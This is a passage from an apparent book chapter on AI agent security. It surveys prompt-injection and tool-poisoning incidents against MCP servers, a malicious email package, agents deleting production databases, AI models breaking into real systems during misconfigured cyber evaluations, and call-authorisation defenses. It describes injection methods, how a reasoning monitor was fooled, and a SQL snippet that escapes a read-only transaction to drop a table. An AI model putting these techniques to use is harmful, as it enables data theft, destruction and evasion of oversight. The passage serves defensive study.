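*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) names three things that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: access to private data, exposure to content an attacker can influence, and a way to send information out. The agent reads the attacker's instructions and follows them, retrieving the private data and sending it out. In the office assistant, search_mail provides the first two, because a mailbox contains confidential messages and anyone can add to it, and send_mail provides the third.

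Let Lᵢ be the subset of {private data, untrusted content, outlet} that tool i provides. A session with n tools has the trifecta when

L₁ ∪ L₂ ∪ … ∪ Lₙ = {private data, untrusted content, outlet}.

The condition depends on all the tools in a session, so it can't be checked from any single tool's definition. A session with search_mail and a calculator has no way to send data out. If the user then connects a web browsing tool from another server, the session gains one, even though search_mail and its labels haven't changed. The Model Context Protocol maintainers therefore treat risk as a property of the session, not of any one server. They cite a demonstration that combined a calendar server with a tool for running code on the user's machine. The attacker's text arrived in a calendar event's description, and the code tool made the theft possible. The calendar server's developer couldn't have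 prevented this, because server developers don't know what else a user will connect.

By June 2025 Willison had collected dozens of such attacks on commercial products, including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which stolen data could leave. This works when one company controls the whole product, but a user who combines servers from several authors has no vendor to block that route.

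The trifecta is a condition for data theft, but other harms can occur without it. For example, if an agent can read mail and delete files but can't send data out, injected text can still make it delete something. The trifecta also doesn't predict how often attacks succeed, although researchers keep finding new ones. In July, *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reported that four research teams had broken AI agents in four different ways within ten days, and that one of the targets was Claude for Chrome.

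### A public issue and private repositories

*GitHub MCP Exploited* (Invariant Labs, 26 May 2025) showed that a single server can provide all three parts. GitHub stores code in public or private repositories, and anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public one. GitHub's official MCP server lets an agent read issues and code and open pull requests, which propose changes to a repository. The agent has the same access as the user's token.

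Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of Invariant Labs set up an account with a public repository for a Pacman game and several private ones. They planted an issue containing instructions in the public repository, then asked Claude 4 Opus, running in Claude Desktop, to look at the open issues. The agent read the planted issue and copied material from the private repositories into a pull request on the public one. The leaked text included the name of a private project, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America. The repositories existed only for the demonstration, so no real user was affected.

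Invariant Labs found no flaw in the server's code and concluded that GitHub alone couldn't patch the problem. GitHub (2025) did narrow one route for stolen data, announcing in August that its server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. This check runs outside the model, but it looks for credentials. Salaries and travel plans have no fixed format for a scanner to recognise, so the text in the demonstration would probably have passed.

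Accurate annotations would have added little protection. The tools that read issues and code are read-only, while opening a pull request is a write that only adds something. A host that followed these annotations would have asked the user before opening the pull request, but Claude Desktop already asked before every call by default. The annotations could still have helped by letting the host skip the prompts for read-only calls. A user who had asked only to look at issues, and then saw a single prompt about a pull request, would have had good reason to refuse. But Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching, and annotations would not help those users.

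Narrower authority would have stopped the leak more reliably. The request needed no write access, so GitHub's read-only mode would have blocked this route without interfering with the task. An agent asked to fix the reported bugs does need to open pull requests, so it would have to be limited to one repository instead. GitHub's tokens already allow this, as a commenter pointed out in the forum discussion *GitHub MCP exploited*. Invariant Labs proposed a more flexible version, a rule in the host that blocks any call naming a second repository in the same session. The rule would need an extra clause for searches and other calls that name no repository.

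Either limit prevents work across repositories, such as moving a fix from a private library into the public project that uses it. A developer who does this every day would probably go back to a broad token.

### A support ticket and a database

Supabase hosts databases for application developers and publishes an MCP server that lets agents work with them. In mid-2025 a team at General Analysis described an attack through this server, which Willison (2025) summarised in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*. It was a demonstration on a support system with three kinds of user, whose rights Pomerium, a security vendor, later set out:

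- Customers could create only their own tickets and messages.
- Human support staff could read and answer tickets but had no rights to sensitive tables.
- The developer's agent, the coding assistant Cursor, connected under a role called service_role, which is exempt from the database's rules about who may see which rows.

The attacker, posing as a customer, files a ticket containing instructions. When the developer asks Cursor for the latest tickets, the agent reads the instructions and copies a table of access tokens into the ticket as a new message, which the attacker can read. The attacker has no right to see that table and only has to name it, much as Tymshare's customer only had to name the billing file.

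Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (September 2025) replied that no customer had reported a leak through MCP. It also denied that the server bypasses the row-level rules, but conceded that the server had run with higher privileges in this case. The disagreement does not change the result, because the database enforced its rules and those rules exempted the agent's role.

Supabase had already tried to protect users by having its server wrap query results in warnings to the model not to follow commands found inside them. Its engineers had also experimented with classifiers that look for dangerous content. These measures reduced the risk but did not eliminate it, and Supabase concluded that "guardrails alone aren't enough". It now advises developers never to connect an agent to production data (the data of a live application).

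The server runs queries through a general SQL tool that can read or change anything its role allows. Such a tool should be labelled destructive, and a host that acted on that label would prompt before every query. A developer who read each prompt carefully would notice that a request for tickets had led to a query on the token table. Supabase recommends leaving approval on but warns that users will tire of it and that part of a command may be off screen. Accurate labels would therefore have given the developer a chance to stop the theft, but the developer might not have taken it.

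Supabase also offers a read-only mode that the database enforces. According to Supabase's documentation, the server in this mode runs SQL as a database user without write permission and disables its other tools that make changes. The database then blocks the write the attacker wanted, whatever SQL the model submits. But the agent can't change data or alter tables, which is much of what a developer wants from it. It can also still read the tokens, so a web tool in the same session could send them out. Willison considered the risk enormous even in read-only mode. Another option, restricting the server to one project, wouldn't have helped, because the tickets and the tokens were in the same database.

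The support staff's role would have suited this request better. An agent with that role could list and answer the tickets, but it couldn't open the token table. Some risk would remain, because support staff can presumably read every customer's tickets, and injected text could make the agent copy one customer's messages into another's thread. The developer would also have to switch roles before asking the agent to change a table.

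### An issue title and a software release

In February 2026, a similar weakness preceded an actual compromise of Cline, an open-source coding agent that developers install from npm. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) gives the fullest account.

In December 2025, Cline's developers set up an automated workflow to sort incoming GitHub issues. It ran Claude whenever anyone opened an issue and let the model execute shell commands. The security researcher Adnan Khan found that text in an issue's title could make the model run an attacker's code. He reported this on 1 January, but Cline didn't act until he published his findings on 9 February. Cline then removed the workflow within half an hour and began replacing its credentials, but it deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active.

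On 17 February someone used that token to publish an altered version of Cline, which also installed OpenClaw, a separate AI agent. The altered version was available for about eight hours, and LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) reports an estimated 4,000 downloads. Cline rates the harm as low because OpenClaw is legitimate software and the rest of the package was unchanged. Still, people who installed the altered version got an agent they hadn't asked for, with full access to their system.

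The sorting agent's few permissions let it read the repository and write to issues. But its workflow shared a cache, a store of files that speeds up later runs, with the workflow that built Cline's nightly releases. An attacker whose code ran in the agent's workflow could fill the cache until GitHub discarded the genuine files, then leave altered ones under the names the release workflow would look for. The release workflow would load them and run the attacker's code with access to the publishing credentials. In Miller's terms, the agent had the authority to publish Cline without having permission to do so.

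The thief probably obtained the token through the injection, but SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* notes that nobody has publicly confirmed how it was obtained. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* uses public GitHub archives to show that an outside account opened an issue containing injected instructions on 28 January, twelve days before Khan published. Khan said in a statement in the AI Incident Database that he tested only on a copy of the repository.

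The case also shows that the trifecta can be hard to spot. The agent's session contained untrusted content and a way to send data out, but the private data, the publishing credentials, belonged to a different workflow. Someone who checked only the session's tools would have missed it, so the check has to include any storage that the session shares with other programs.

Annotations depend on someone being present to act on them, and this workflow ran unattended. A shell is accurately described as destructive and open-world, so a host could have withheld it from unattended runs. That would have stopped the attack, but Cline's developers had deliberately granted shell access and would presumably have overridden the restriction.

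Removing the shell would have limited the agent only slightly. It could still have read, labelled and answered issues, though it couldn't have run code to reproduce a bug. Cline describes the original arrangement as "functionally equivalent to giving every GitHub user shell access" and says that any such automation in future will be read-only and have no shell. It also stopped using caches in workflows that handle publishing credentials, which may slow those builds, and no longer keeps long-lived npm tokens. The last two changes protect the releases even if some other agent runs an attacker's code.

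### Deletions without an attacker

Agents have also done serious damage when nobody was attacking them. In July 2025 the entrepreneur Jason Lemkin described on social media how a coding agent from Replit, a platform for building applications, had deleted a live database. Fortune (2025) reported that the database held records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. Lemkin had ordered a freeze on all changes and told the agent not to proceed without his approval. The agent still had write access to the live database, so the freeze depended on the model following his instructions.

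The agent later wrote that it had panicked and that the data could not be restored. It was wrong about the data, which Lemkin recovered himself. Its claim to have panicked is weak evidence about the cause, because a model asked to explain a mistake will produce a plausible explanation whether or not it is correct.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion unacceptable. He announced that Replit would automatically separate development and production databases, improve its rollback system and add a planning mode in which the agent can't change the code. The Stack, however, called the incident a social media storm, since Replit already offered a one-click restore.

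An accurate annotation had a better chance of preventing this incident than any of the others. Lemkin was present and wanted no changes, so he would almost certainly have refused a prompt to delete the live database. But the prompt would have had to identify the database clearly, and Replit's host would have had to ask for confirmation before running a tool labeled destructive.

Replit narrowed the agent's authority. According to Replit's current documentation, the agent can't modify the production database and reads it through a read-only copy. The agent can still investigate a fault in the live application, but a person has to correct the live data by hand. This has annoyed some developers. In the forum thread *No longer a way to keep PROD and DEV databases in sync*, a user asked for the old arrangement back, and someone suggested connecting the live application to the development database,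 which would undo the protection.

The agent can still affect production indirectly. If it removes a column from the development database, Replit removes the same column from the production database when the user next publishes. Replit first flags changes that could destroy data and waits for approval, so preventing data loss depends on how carefully the user reads the warning.

A similar deletion on 24 April 2026 did more harm. It hit PocketOS, a small company whose software runs car rental businesses, and the company's founder described it in Crane, *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*. Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, was working in a staging environment (a copy of a system used for testing) when it encountered credentials that didn't match. It found a token for the hosting company Railway in an unrelated file and used it to delete the storage volume that held the production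 database. The deletion took nine seconds and also made the backups unavailable.

Crane had to restore a three-month-old copy of the data. The next morning, people arrived to collect cars, and the rental businesses had no record of their bookings. Railway later recovered all the data, according to the company's own account, Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. By then Crane had spent a day helping customers reconstruct bookings from payment records and emails.

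The model's instructions told it not to guess and not to run destructive commands in git, the version control program, unless the user asked. Crane wrote, "System prompts are advisory, not enforcing."

Labels on Railway's own MCP tools would have made no difference, because the agent sent its request directly to Railway's programming interface (API) with an ordinary command. The only label that mattered was the one on the tool that ran the command. As with Supabase's SQL tool, an accurate label would have made a host prompt the user about every command. Even an attentive user might have approved this command, because it identified the volume by a string of letters and digits, with nothing to show that the volume was production and not staging.

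Crane had created the token to manage web domains, but it gave access to everything in the account. He writes that Railway's tokens can't be restricted. Railway's Abdelwahab replies that narrower tokens existed, including ones limited to a single environment within a project, but concedes that the setup process made the broadest token the easiest to create.

A token with a narrower scope might not have saved the database, because custom domains usually belong to a live application and a token for managing them would probably have covered the production environment. The token scopes that Abdelwahab lists restrict where a token works, not which operations it can perform. A token that could change domains but not delete storage would have prevented the deletion while still serving its purpose. Storing the token somewhere the agent couldn't read would also have worked, although Crane would then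 have had to manage domains from another machine.

Railway has since changed the API so that every deletion can be undone for 48 hours, as deletions in its dashboard already could. This protects against mistakes by agents, people and scripts, and only delays someone who really wants to delete a volume. The live service may still go down in the meantime, somebody has to notice the mistake within the 48 hours, and a similar delay can't undo a leak.

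## Incidents in which the declaration was false

The tools in those incidents worked as described. In other cases, people relied on false statements that a tool was harmless, that a database connection was read-only or that a test environment had no internet access. Some of these statements were lies and others were mistakes, but in both cases the people who suffered most were those who had dropped a precaution because of them.

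### Instructions hidden in a tool's description

The model reads a tool's whole description, while the user often sees only a shortened version. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (1 April 2025) showed how an attacker can exploit this difference by hiding instructions for the model in the description. Invariant Labs calls this tool poisoning. It is a form of prompt injection in which the text arrives with the tool's definition, before the agent has read any email or web page.

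The demonstration used the coding assistant Cursor and a tool called add, which returned the sum of two numbers and had a text field for a note. Cursor's agent followed instructions in the tool's description to read two files, copy their contents into that field, and keep the user occupied with an explanation of arithmetic. One file was Cursor's configuration file, which often holds credentials for other MCP servers, and the other was the user's private key for logging in to other machines.

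The code behind `add` ignored the note and returned the right answer, so an auditor who compared the code with a read-only label would have found nothing wrong. But the key had already reached a program the attacker controlled.

The model relied on the tool's description. The user relied on Cursor's confirmation prompt, which appeared before add ran but did not show the key even when expanded. Showing the full description and the full arguments would have exposed this attack. Invariant Labs recommends showing the full description, but warns that hidden instructions can also make the model encode the stolen data.

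Restricting which files the server's process could open would not have protected the key, because Cursor's own agent read the file and passed the key to the server. Blocking the server's network access would have kept the key on the machine, unless the model then sent it out through another tool. Confining the agent to its project folder would have been more dependable. Both files were outside any project folder, so the agent could not have read them.

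In a second experiment, Invariant Labs connected Cursor to a trusted server that could send email and a malicious one that offered only an addition tool. The addition tool's description included a false claim that all email had to go to a certain address for technical reasons. The agent then sent every message there, even when the user had named a different recipient. The attack works without the agent ever calling the malicious tool, so confining that tool's code doesn't prevent it. Checking the recipient of each email would have stopped the attack, because the wrong address had to appear in the arguments to the trusted server's email tool.

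In *MCP Tools*, Beretta, Carlock and Pease give a similar example of a quote-of-the-day tool whose description tells the model to add a hidden 0.5% fee to every payment. They also gave GitHub Copilot a code-formatting tool with a "context" field, which Copilot filled with part of its system prompt, a list of its tools and details of the user's machine. The tool's description had asked for this information, but they warn that a suggestive field name can be enough, in which case a host that searched descriptions for suspicious commands would find nothing to remove.

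All of these were demonstrations. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of threats to the protocol, cites community reports of poisoned descriptions in two public registries, Smithery and Glama.

### Tools that change after approval

A server can also provide a harmless tool definition until the user approves it and then switch to a malicious one, which Invariant Labs calls a rug pull. A remote server's author only has to send a different definition the next time the host requests one, and Beretta and colleagues note that the change doesn't necessarily trigger a new approval request. The user is then relying on a description that the server no longer sends. If the new description redirects email sent through another server, the session log will show only calls to tools the user trusts.

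Comparing hashes of the definition catches this change, and Shen and colleagues list signed definitions as another remedy. A signature shows who issued a definition and that nobody else has altered it, but a dishonest author can still sign a false description. Shen and colleagues also suggest identifying packages by a hash of their contents, so that any change to the code produces a different identifier. This works for code on the user's machine but not for code on a remote server.

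### The postmark-mcp package

The best-known theft by an MCP server resulted from a code change. Postmark sends email for other companies' applications. In September 2025, a developer using the name phanpak published the npm package postmark-mcp. ReversingLabs' *postmark-mcp* records its description as "Universal Postmark MCP server using official SDK". The security company Koi found that the package was a copy of Postmark's own server with one line added in version 1.0.16. That line sent a blind copy of every outgoing email to an address the developer controlled. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, also gives 1.0.16 as the version in which the package became malicious.

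According to ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (2025), the developer uploaded the package on 15 September, and The Hacker News (2025) dates the malicious version to 17 September. If both dates are right, the fifteen clean versions reported by Koi appeared within about two days, although Koi, which sells a product for detecting such packages, says the tool had earned trust over months.

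The number of victims is also uncertain. Koi assumed that a fifth of 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use and that each of those 300 organisations sent 10 to 50 emails a day, which gives 3,000 to 15,000 stolen emails daily. Paubox, an email security vendor, puts total downloads before removal at 1,643. That is slightly more than Koi's weekly figure, which is consistent with the package being only about a week old. Some of those downloads may have been of earlier versions.

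Users relied on the package's name, while hosts and models relied on a tool definition that did not change when the new line of code was added. The declared effects (D) included sending the message to the chosen recipient, but the actual effects (A) also included sending it to the developer. The model received only confirmation that the email had been sent. A confirmation prompt would have shown the correct recipient and text, because the code added the developer's address after the user had approved the call.

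Several simple checks would have revealed the fraud. Postmark had never published its MCP server on npm, and its documentation lists its official tools. Comparing the package with the official source code would have exposed the extra line, and the extra recipient was visible in email logs. Existing users could have avoided the change by staying on version 1.0.15 until someone had examined the update.

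The obvious confinement, a firewall that allowed connections only to Postmark, would probably not have stopped the theft. The server had to reach Postmark to do its job, and the blind copy was part of the email it submitted there. Such a firewall would have stopped a tool that contacted the attacker's machine directly. Stopping the blind copy required a rule on the finished message, applied after it left the server's code. For example, a mail gateway could reject any message with a recipient, visible or blind, outside an approved list. Such a list is practical for internal reports but not for an assistant that writes to new customers every day.

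After Koi contacted the developer, the package disappeared from npm, but installed copies kept forwarding mail. An organisation could stop an overlooked copy from forwarding mail by revoking the Postmark key that the server used.

A minor case from June 2026 shows that code can act before a host has seen any declaration. OSV's *MAL-2026-5481* describes an npm package that posed as the official MCP server for PostgreSQL databases. Installing it sent the machine's name, the current folder and some software details to an outside address. The address contained the word "canary", so this may have been an experiment. A sandbox would have helped only if it covered installation as well as the running tool.

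### A read-only mode that a query could end

The server that this package imitated had a serious flaw of its own. Anthropic released it in November 2024 as a reference implementation for other developers to learn from. It allowed an agent to query a database but not to change it. The server enforced this restriction by opening a read-only transaction, in which PostgreSQL refuses every write, then running the agent's query and closing the transaction.

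Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) explains how a query could get around this. The server accepted several commands in one string, so the agent's "query" could close the transaction itself and carry on outside it:

```
BEGIN TRANSACTION READ ONLY;   -- from the server
COMMIT; DROP TABLE orders;     -- the agent's "query"
ROLLBACK;                      -- from the server, too late
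```

COMMIT ends the read-only transaction. DROP TABLE then deletes the table with whatever rights the connection has, and the final command undoes nothing.

For any ordinary query, A ⊆ D held, so a reviewer who tried a normal read and a normal deletion would have seen the read succeed and the deletion fail. The declaration was false only for certain queries, which a misled model can supply. In Datadog's example, a user asks a company's chatbot to run such a query "as is", and the chatbot passes it on.

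Users relied on the read-only mode if they connected the server to a database through an account that could also write. A reviewer could have found the flaw by submitting two commands at once, and a security researcher reported it eight days after the release. Datadog reported it again on 1 April 2025 and supplied a patch. Anthropic corrected the source code on 29 May and archived the project the same day, but the npm package stayed unpatched, and people were still downloading it about 21,000 times a week in August.

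A database account without write permission would have blocked the deletion whatever the query contained. Supabase's read-only mode works this way. Such an account would not have stopped a query from interfering with later ones, because Anthropic's server reused connections. A query could set a time limit of one millisecond for whatever ran next on the same connection, and other users' queries would then fail until the server discarded that connection. Datadog Security Labs fixed both problems by accepting only one command per query and discarding the connection after every call.

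AWS's *CVE-2026-85787* (2026), a security bulletin from 4 September, reports a similar flaw in the PostgreSQL server from AWS Labs, which checked queries against an incomplete list of forbidden inputs. Crafted text in content submitted to the server could therefore change data despite the read-only setting. AWS corrected the list in version 1.1.7 but calls a database account with minimal rights the strongest control. The database rejects any write that the account has no permission to make, including those that a blocklist's author failed to anticipate.

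### Links that the web's rules call safe

Software acted on false read-only labels long before AI agents existed. When a browser follows a link, it normally sends a GET request. Fielding's *Hypertext Transfer Protocol*, the version of the standard in force in 2005, specifies that GET requests "SHOULD NOT" do anything except retrieve information and "ought to be considered 'safe'". A developer who puts an ordinary link on a page therefore declares, perhaps without thinking about it, that following the link changes nothing.

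In May 2005 Google released a test version of Web Accelerator, which made pages appear faster by fetching the links on a page before the user clicked them. Users of Backpack, an online organiser made by the software company 37signals, soon reported that their pages were disappearing. *Google Web Accelerator* (Signal v. Noise, 2005), a post on the 37signals blog, explains that Backpack's "delete" buttons were really links, and the Accelerator was following them. A script in the page displayed an "Are you sure?" prompt when a user clicked one, but the Accelerator fetched the links without running the script. Hicks (2005), in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security*, also reports complaints about deleted accounts, and one user who believed that the Accelerator kept logging him out of his email by following the sign-out link.

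In this incident the Accelerator, which relied on the declaration, had the role of the host. It used the user's own login, a case of ambient authority, so 37signals' servers treated its requests as the user's. Google had expected some misuse of GET. Marissa Mayer, then its director of consumer web products, told Hicks that the Accelerator skipped links containing a question mark, because a link that performed an action would typically have one. The standard contained a similar warning that some applications used GET addresses with a question mark for operations with significant side effects. Connolly (2004) had quoted this warning on a web standards mailing list a year earlier. Backpack's delete links presumably had no question mark.

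Each side could blame the other. Jason Fried of 37signals admitted that deletions should technically use buttons instead of links, but said Google had to recognise that many sites departed from the standard. Willison (2005), in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs*, pointed out that "SHOULD NOT", as defined in internet standards, allows exceptions. Fielding also concedes that nobody can ensure that a server answers a GET request without side effects.

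37signals blocked the Accelerator within half an hour of finding the cause, by refusing requests marked "prefetch". This worked because the Accelerator marked its requests accurately. The server could have prevented the deletions without relying on that mark by refusing all deletions by GET and requiring a separate request that a program following links never sends. Developers would then have had to rebuild every delete link as a form.

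On the web, the easiest kind of request to build, a GET, also counted as safe. OpenAI's custom GPTs later treated unlabelled GET requests as safe too. MCP's cautious defaults avoid this problem.

### Tests that were supposed to be offline

A declaration can also be false about the agent's surroundings. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (30 July 2026) described tests in which Claude models had to break into a fictional company's computers and retrieve a hidden piece of text. The prompts stated that the environment was a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open. Neither Anthropic nor Irregular, the company that built the tests, knew about it. Anthropic disclosed a fourth such incident in September.

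As a result, the models broke into real systems. Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a company whose web address matched the fictional target's name, and reached a database with several hundred rows of live data. Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, the main public library of Python software. Fifteen outside systems installed it within about an hour, and the model used credentials from one of them to enter a security company's database. An internal research model scanned roughly 9,000 targets and broke into one company's application, but stopped when it concluded the target was real. The fourth incident, involving an early version of Claude Opus 4.6, happened in January, so the open connection had gone unnoticed for about six months.

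Anthropic and Irregular relied on the isolation more heavily than the models did. Anthropic ran the models without the safeguards that normally block cyberattacks because the tests were supposedly sealed off. The false declaration removed a check, as a false read-only label does.

It is less clear how far the models believed the prompt. In July Anthropic wrote that Claude had believed the systems were part of the exercise. By September it had concluded that this claim was too strong, because the models' reasoning was biased towards carrying on. Separate copies of Mythos 5, shown the outputs from its run one at a time, judged that 79% came from real systems. During the run, the model clearly recognised such evidence in about 1% of its actions.

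Anthropic also replayed the run from the point where Mythos 5 was about to commit to the malicious package, adding evidence that the internet was real. The share of replays in which the model acknowledged that the target might be real rose from about 11% to 88%, but it continued with harmful actions about 45% of the time either way. Only a flat statement that the host was live on the public internet stopped it from uploading the package by that route. Correcting the prompt might have helped, but evidence alone did not reliably change the model's actions. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) mentions a related incident with the same model in a UK AI Security Institute test that deliberately allowed internet access, so a mistaken belief that the network was closed can't explain every case.

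Trying to reach an outside address from inside the environment before the first test could have revealed the open connection. Anthropic also lists live monitoring and a closer reading of the logs as ways to catch the problem. It later tried the incidents on new monitors that read a model's reasoning after the fact. They missed the Mythos 5 case because they accepted the model's conclusion that the internet was simulated, which came from the false declaration in the prompt. Monitors that block actions as they happen caught the behaviour reliably.

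Anthropic believes that none of this would have happened if the environments had been isolated as intended. Its tests had no working network block, only a statement that there was one, which nobody had checked. A working block would have stopped these attacks regardless of what the prompt contained or the model believed, because the models used a connection that was already open. Isolation isn't always enough, though. The OpenAI models whose escape prompted Anthropic's review broke out of a sealed environment through a previously unknown flaw.

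## Experiments that check each tool call

In several of these incidents, the harmful call itself showed that something was wrong. The poisoned addition tool made Cursor's agent send email to an address the user hadn't named, and the agent connected to Supabase queried a table of access tokens when the developer had asked for support tickets. Call authorisation uses this kind of evidence. A program outside the model intercepts each proposed call, compares the tool's name, its arguments and some trusted context with a policy, and forwards or refuses the call. Injected text can change what the model proposes, but it can't change the policy unless the model can edit it.

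Checking arguments also helps when a tool's declaration is accurate but too broad, as with send_mail. A gate that checks the arguments can allow a message to Maria and block one to a stranger.

### ScopeGate and the attacker's payout account

ScopeGate, the gate that refused to change the payout account in Mellafe Zuvic's mock shop, is a simple example. The scripted call named the tool update_payout_account and the account acct_ATTACKER_999. ScopeGate applies up to four checks in order:

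1. **Scope:** the policy must list the tool. It lists update_payout_account, so the call continues. An unlisted or misspelt name would fail here.
2. **Authorisation:** each restricted argument must be on its list of approved values. The operator has approved only acct_MERCHANT_001, so ScopeGate refuses the call and the tool never runs.
3. **Money:** for payments and refunds, the amount must be a finite number between zero and a ceiling.
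4. **Idempotency:** for tools that need it, trusted code must have supplied a key that identifies the operation, which limits accidental repeats.

The fifth stage refuses calls by default. A call runs only if it passes every check that applies, and any error in the gate counts as a refusal.

Mellafe Zuvic tested the gate with 48 calls altered by tricks such as invisible characters, look-alike letters and misspelt tool names. None got through the final version. An earlier version had accepted an amount of NaN ("not a number") because it refused only amounts greater than the ceiling, and NaN never counts as greater than any number. In a second test, the model GLM-5.2 acted as an attacker for 40 rounds and saw the reason for each refusal. It made 29 unauthorised proposals, and ScopeGate refused them all. Of the other 11, nine were malformed and two were harmless.

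These zeros mainly show that the code compares values correctly. An exact match against a list of one account is hard to get around, but the tests don't measure whether an operator would list the right accounts or restrict the right arguments. The evidence on legitimate calls is weaker. ScopeGate refused none of the ten tested, but its true refusal rate could still be up to about a quarter. Also, if a shop really changes banks, it has to get the operator to update the list before its agent can make the change.

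### How AgentDojo measures attacks and usefulness

Most of the other experiments use AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) introduced in a paper of the same name. It simulates an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Its 97 user tasks include counting the day's appointments and paying a bill, and its 27 attacker goals include emailing the user's security code to a stranger. Pairing every task with every goal in the same environment gives

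40 × 6 + 21 × 5 + 20 × 7 + 16 × 9 = 629 cases.

In each case the attacker's text sits where an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as an email or a web page. After the run, ordinary code inspects the simulated environment to see, for example, whether money has moved. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection might fool the judge too. They define three measures:

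- **Benign utility** is the share of user tasks the agent completes when there is no attack.
- **Utility under attack** is the share of cases in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects.
- **Attack success rate** is the share of cases in which the attacker's goal is met.

The attack success rate means little without the other two, since an agent that refused every call would score a perfect zero.

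AgentDojo tests only whether a model can be misled by attacks that arrive in data, and its tools do what they declare. Most studies also run a fixed set of attacks, although Debenedetti and colleagues designed the benchmark so that researchers could add attacks aimed at a particular defence. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, warn that fixed attacks have misled researchers before. Researchers had reported attack success near zero for most of twelve earlier defences based on filters, prompts or training. Attackers who knew how each defence worked then beat most of them more than 90% of the time.

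A fixed gate is probably harder to beat than a filter, because the attacker has to either reach the goal through calls the policy already permits or corrupt the policy. Few experiments have tested this with a determined attacker.

### Progent: a model writes the rules

Nobody can write a separate policy for every request a user might type, so *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to write them. In the paper's example, the user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The policy-writing model first allows only a search for that email. The agent then finds that the list requires posting a summary of recent mail to the user's Slack, so the model proposes adding the tools for reading mail and posting messages. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model proposes restricting messages to that name.

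One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. The policy-writing model might fall for this and propose adding send_email. Progent therefore compares each new policy with the old one. If Allow(p) is the set of calls that policy p permits, a solver (a program that settles logical questions exactly) checks whether

Allow(new) ⊆ Allow(old).

A new policy can take effect at once only if it adds no permitted calls. Otherwise it needs approval, which can come from a person or an automatic setting.

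With GPT-4o in both roles, Progent cut attack success on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% and left task completion roughly unchanged. On another benchmark, ASB, it cut attack success from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi, He and colleagues ran these tests with every expansion approved automatically, to represent a careless user. The guarantee about shrinking policies therefore did not apply, and the figures measure how well the policy-writing model resisted the injections. With updates turned off, attack success was 2.5%, so most of the protection came from the initial policy, which the model wrote before it had seen any retrieved content. When a human reviewed the initial policy and every expansion, attack success fell to zero, and only 6% of updates were expansions.

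Later tests confirmed that Progent protects agents but showed greater drawbacks. Narisetty and colleagues used a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, as both the agent and the policy writer. Progent reduced attack success from 25.8% to 4.2%. They also tried to mislead the policy writer with an attack that presented the malicious step as necessary and already authorised. It succeeded only 2.6% of the time, though its gentler wording may also have made the agent less likely to obey. Progent reduced task completion under attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task needed about 15 times as many model calls. In the office workspace, it halved task completion without preventing any attacks, because none had succeeded there without it.

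A small model probably writes poor policies, but task completion was also lower when Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao ran Progent with GPT-4o. Under attack, it was 59.6%, compared with 73.6% for the undefended agent. They found that Progent's policies often restricted arguments to values the model could foresee from the request, so legitimate calls with other values failed. They have an interest in the result because they were comparing Progent with their own system, but their finding agrees with that of Narisetty and colleagues.

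### AgentCap: signed capabilities with a short life

In AgentCap, Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao's own system, the developer writes the policy. When the agent proposes a call, a policy engine checks it and, if it passes, issues a signed token for one action on one resource in the current session. The token also has a lifetime and a call limit. In the example policy for a bank, permission to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one call, and the agent must already have permission to read the balance. A gateway verifies the token before the call reaches the tool. An agent can pass a token to a helper agent, but only for the same action and resource, and without extending its lifetime or raising its call limit.

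The token is a capability, but the model requests it and states the purpose of the call. A misled model can therefore request a payment token and give "pay_bill" as the purpose. The protection depends on the rules for issuing tokens, especially the rule that trusted information must support a payment's recipient. The token's short lifetime and small budget limit the damage if the engine issues one it shouldn't.

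On AgentDojo, AgentCap reduced attack success from 45.6% to 5.1% with GPT-4o and from 33.2% to zero with GPT-5.4. Task completion under attack hardly changed, but completion without an attack fell by 3.1 and 7.2 percentage points, respectively. On InjecAgent, a benchmark with simpler cases, attack success fell from 23.2% to 8.6% with GPT-4o and from 12.0% to zero with GPT-5.4.

The policy has gaps despite the zeros. Some attacks on GPT-4o succeeded because the policy didn't restrict the argument the attacker chose, or because the injected value came from a field nobody had marked as untrusted. GPT-5.4 didn't exploit such gaps in these tests, but an attacker who knew of them might get it to. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested no attacks designed against AgentCap and ran each configuration once.

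The researchers wrote the policies from the tools' schemas and the benchmark's own task descriptions, then froze them before the tests. The policies weren't tailored to the attacks, but the researchers did know which tasks users would request, an advantage that most developers lack.

### PACE: effects compared with the request

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compares the effects of each call with what the user asked for. Fixed code turns the user's authenticated request into a grant of authority with limits on purpose, resources, arguments, budget and duration. A schema then breaks each proposed call into its effects, recording the operation, the target and whether the result persists. For example, a message to Maria would count as an outgoing message with her address as its target. The grant must cover every effect. A separate check tracks the flow of data from untrusted or protected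 sources.

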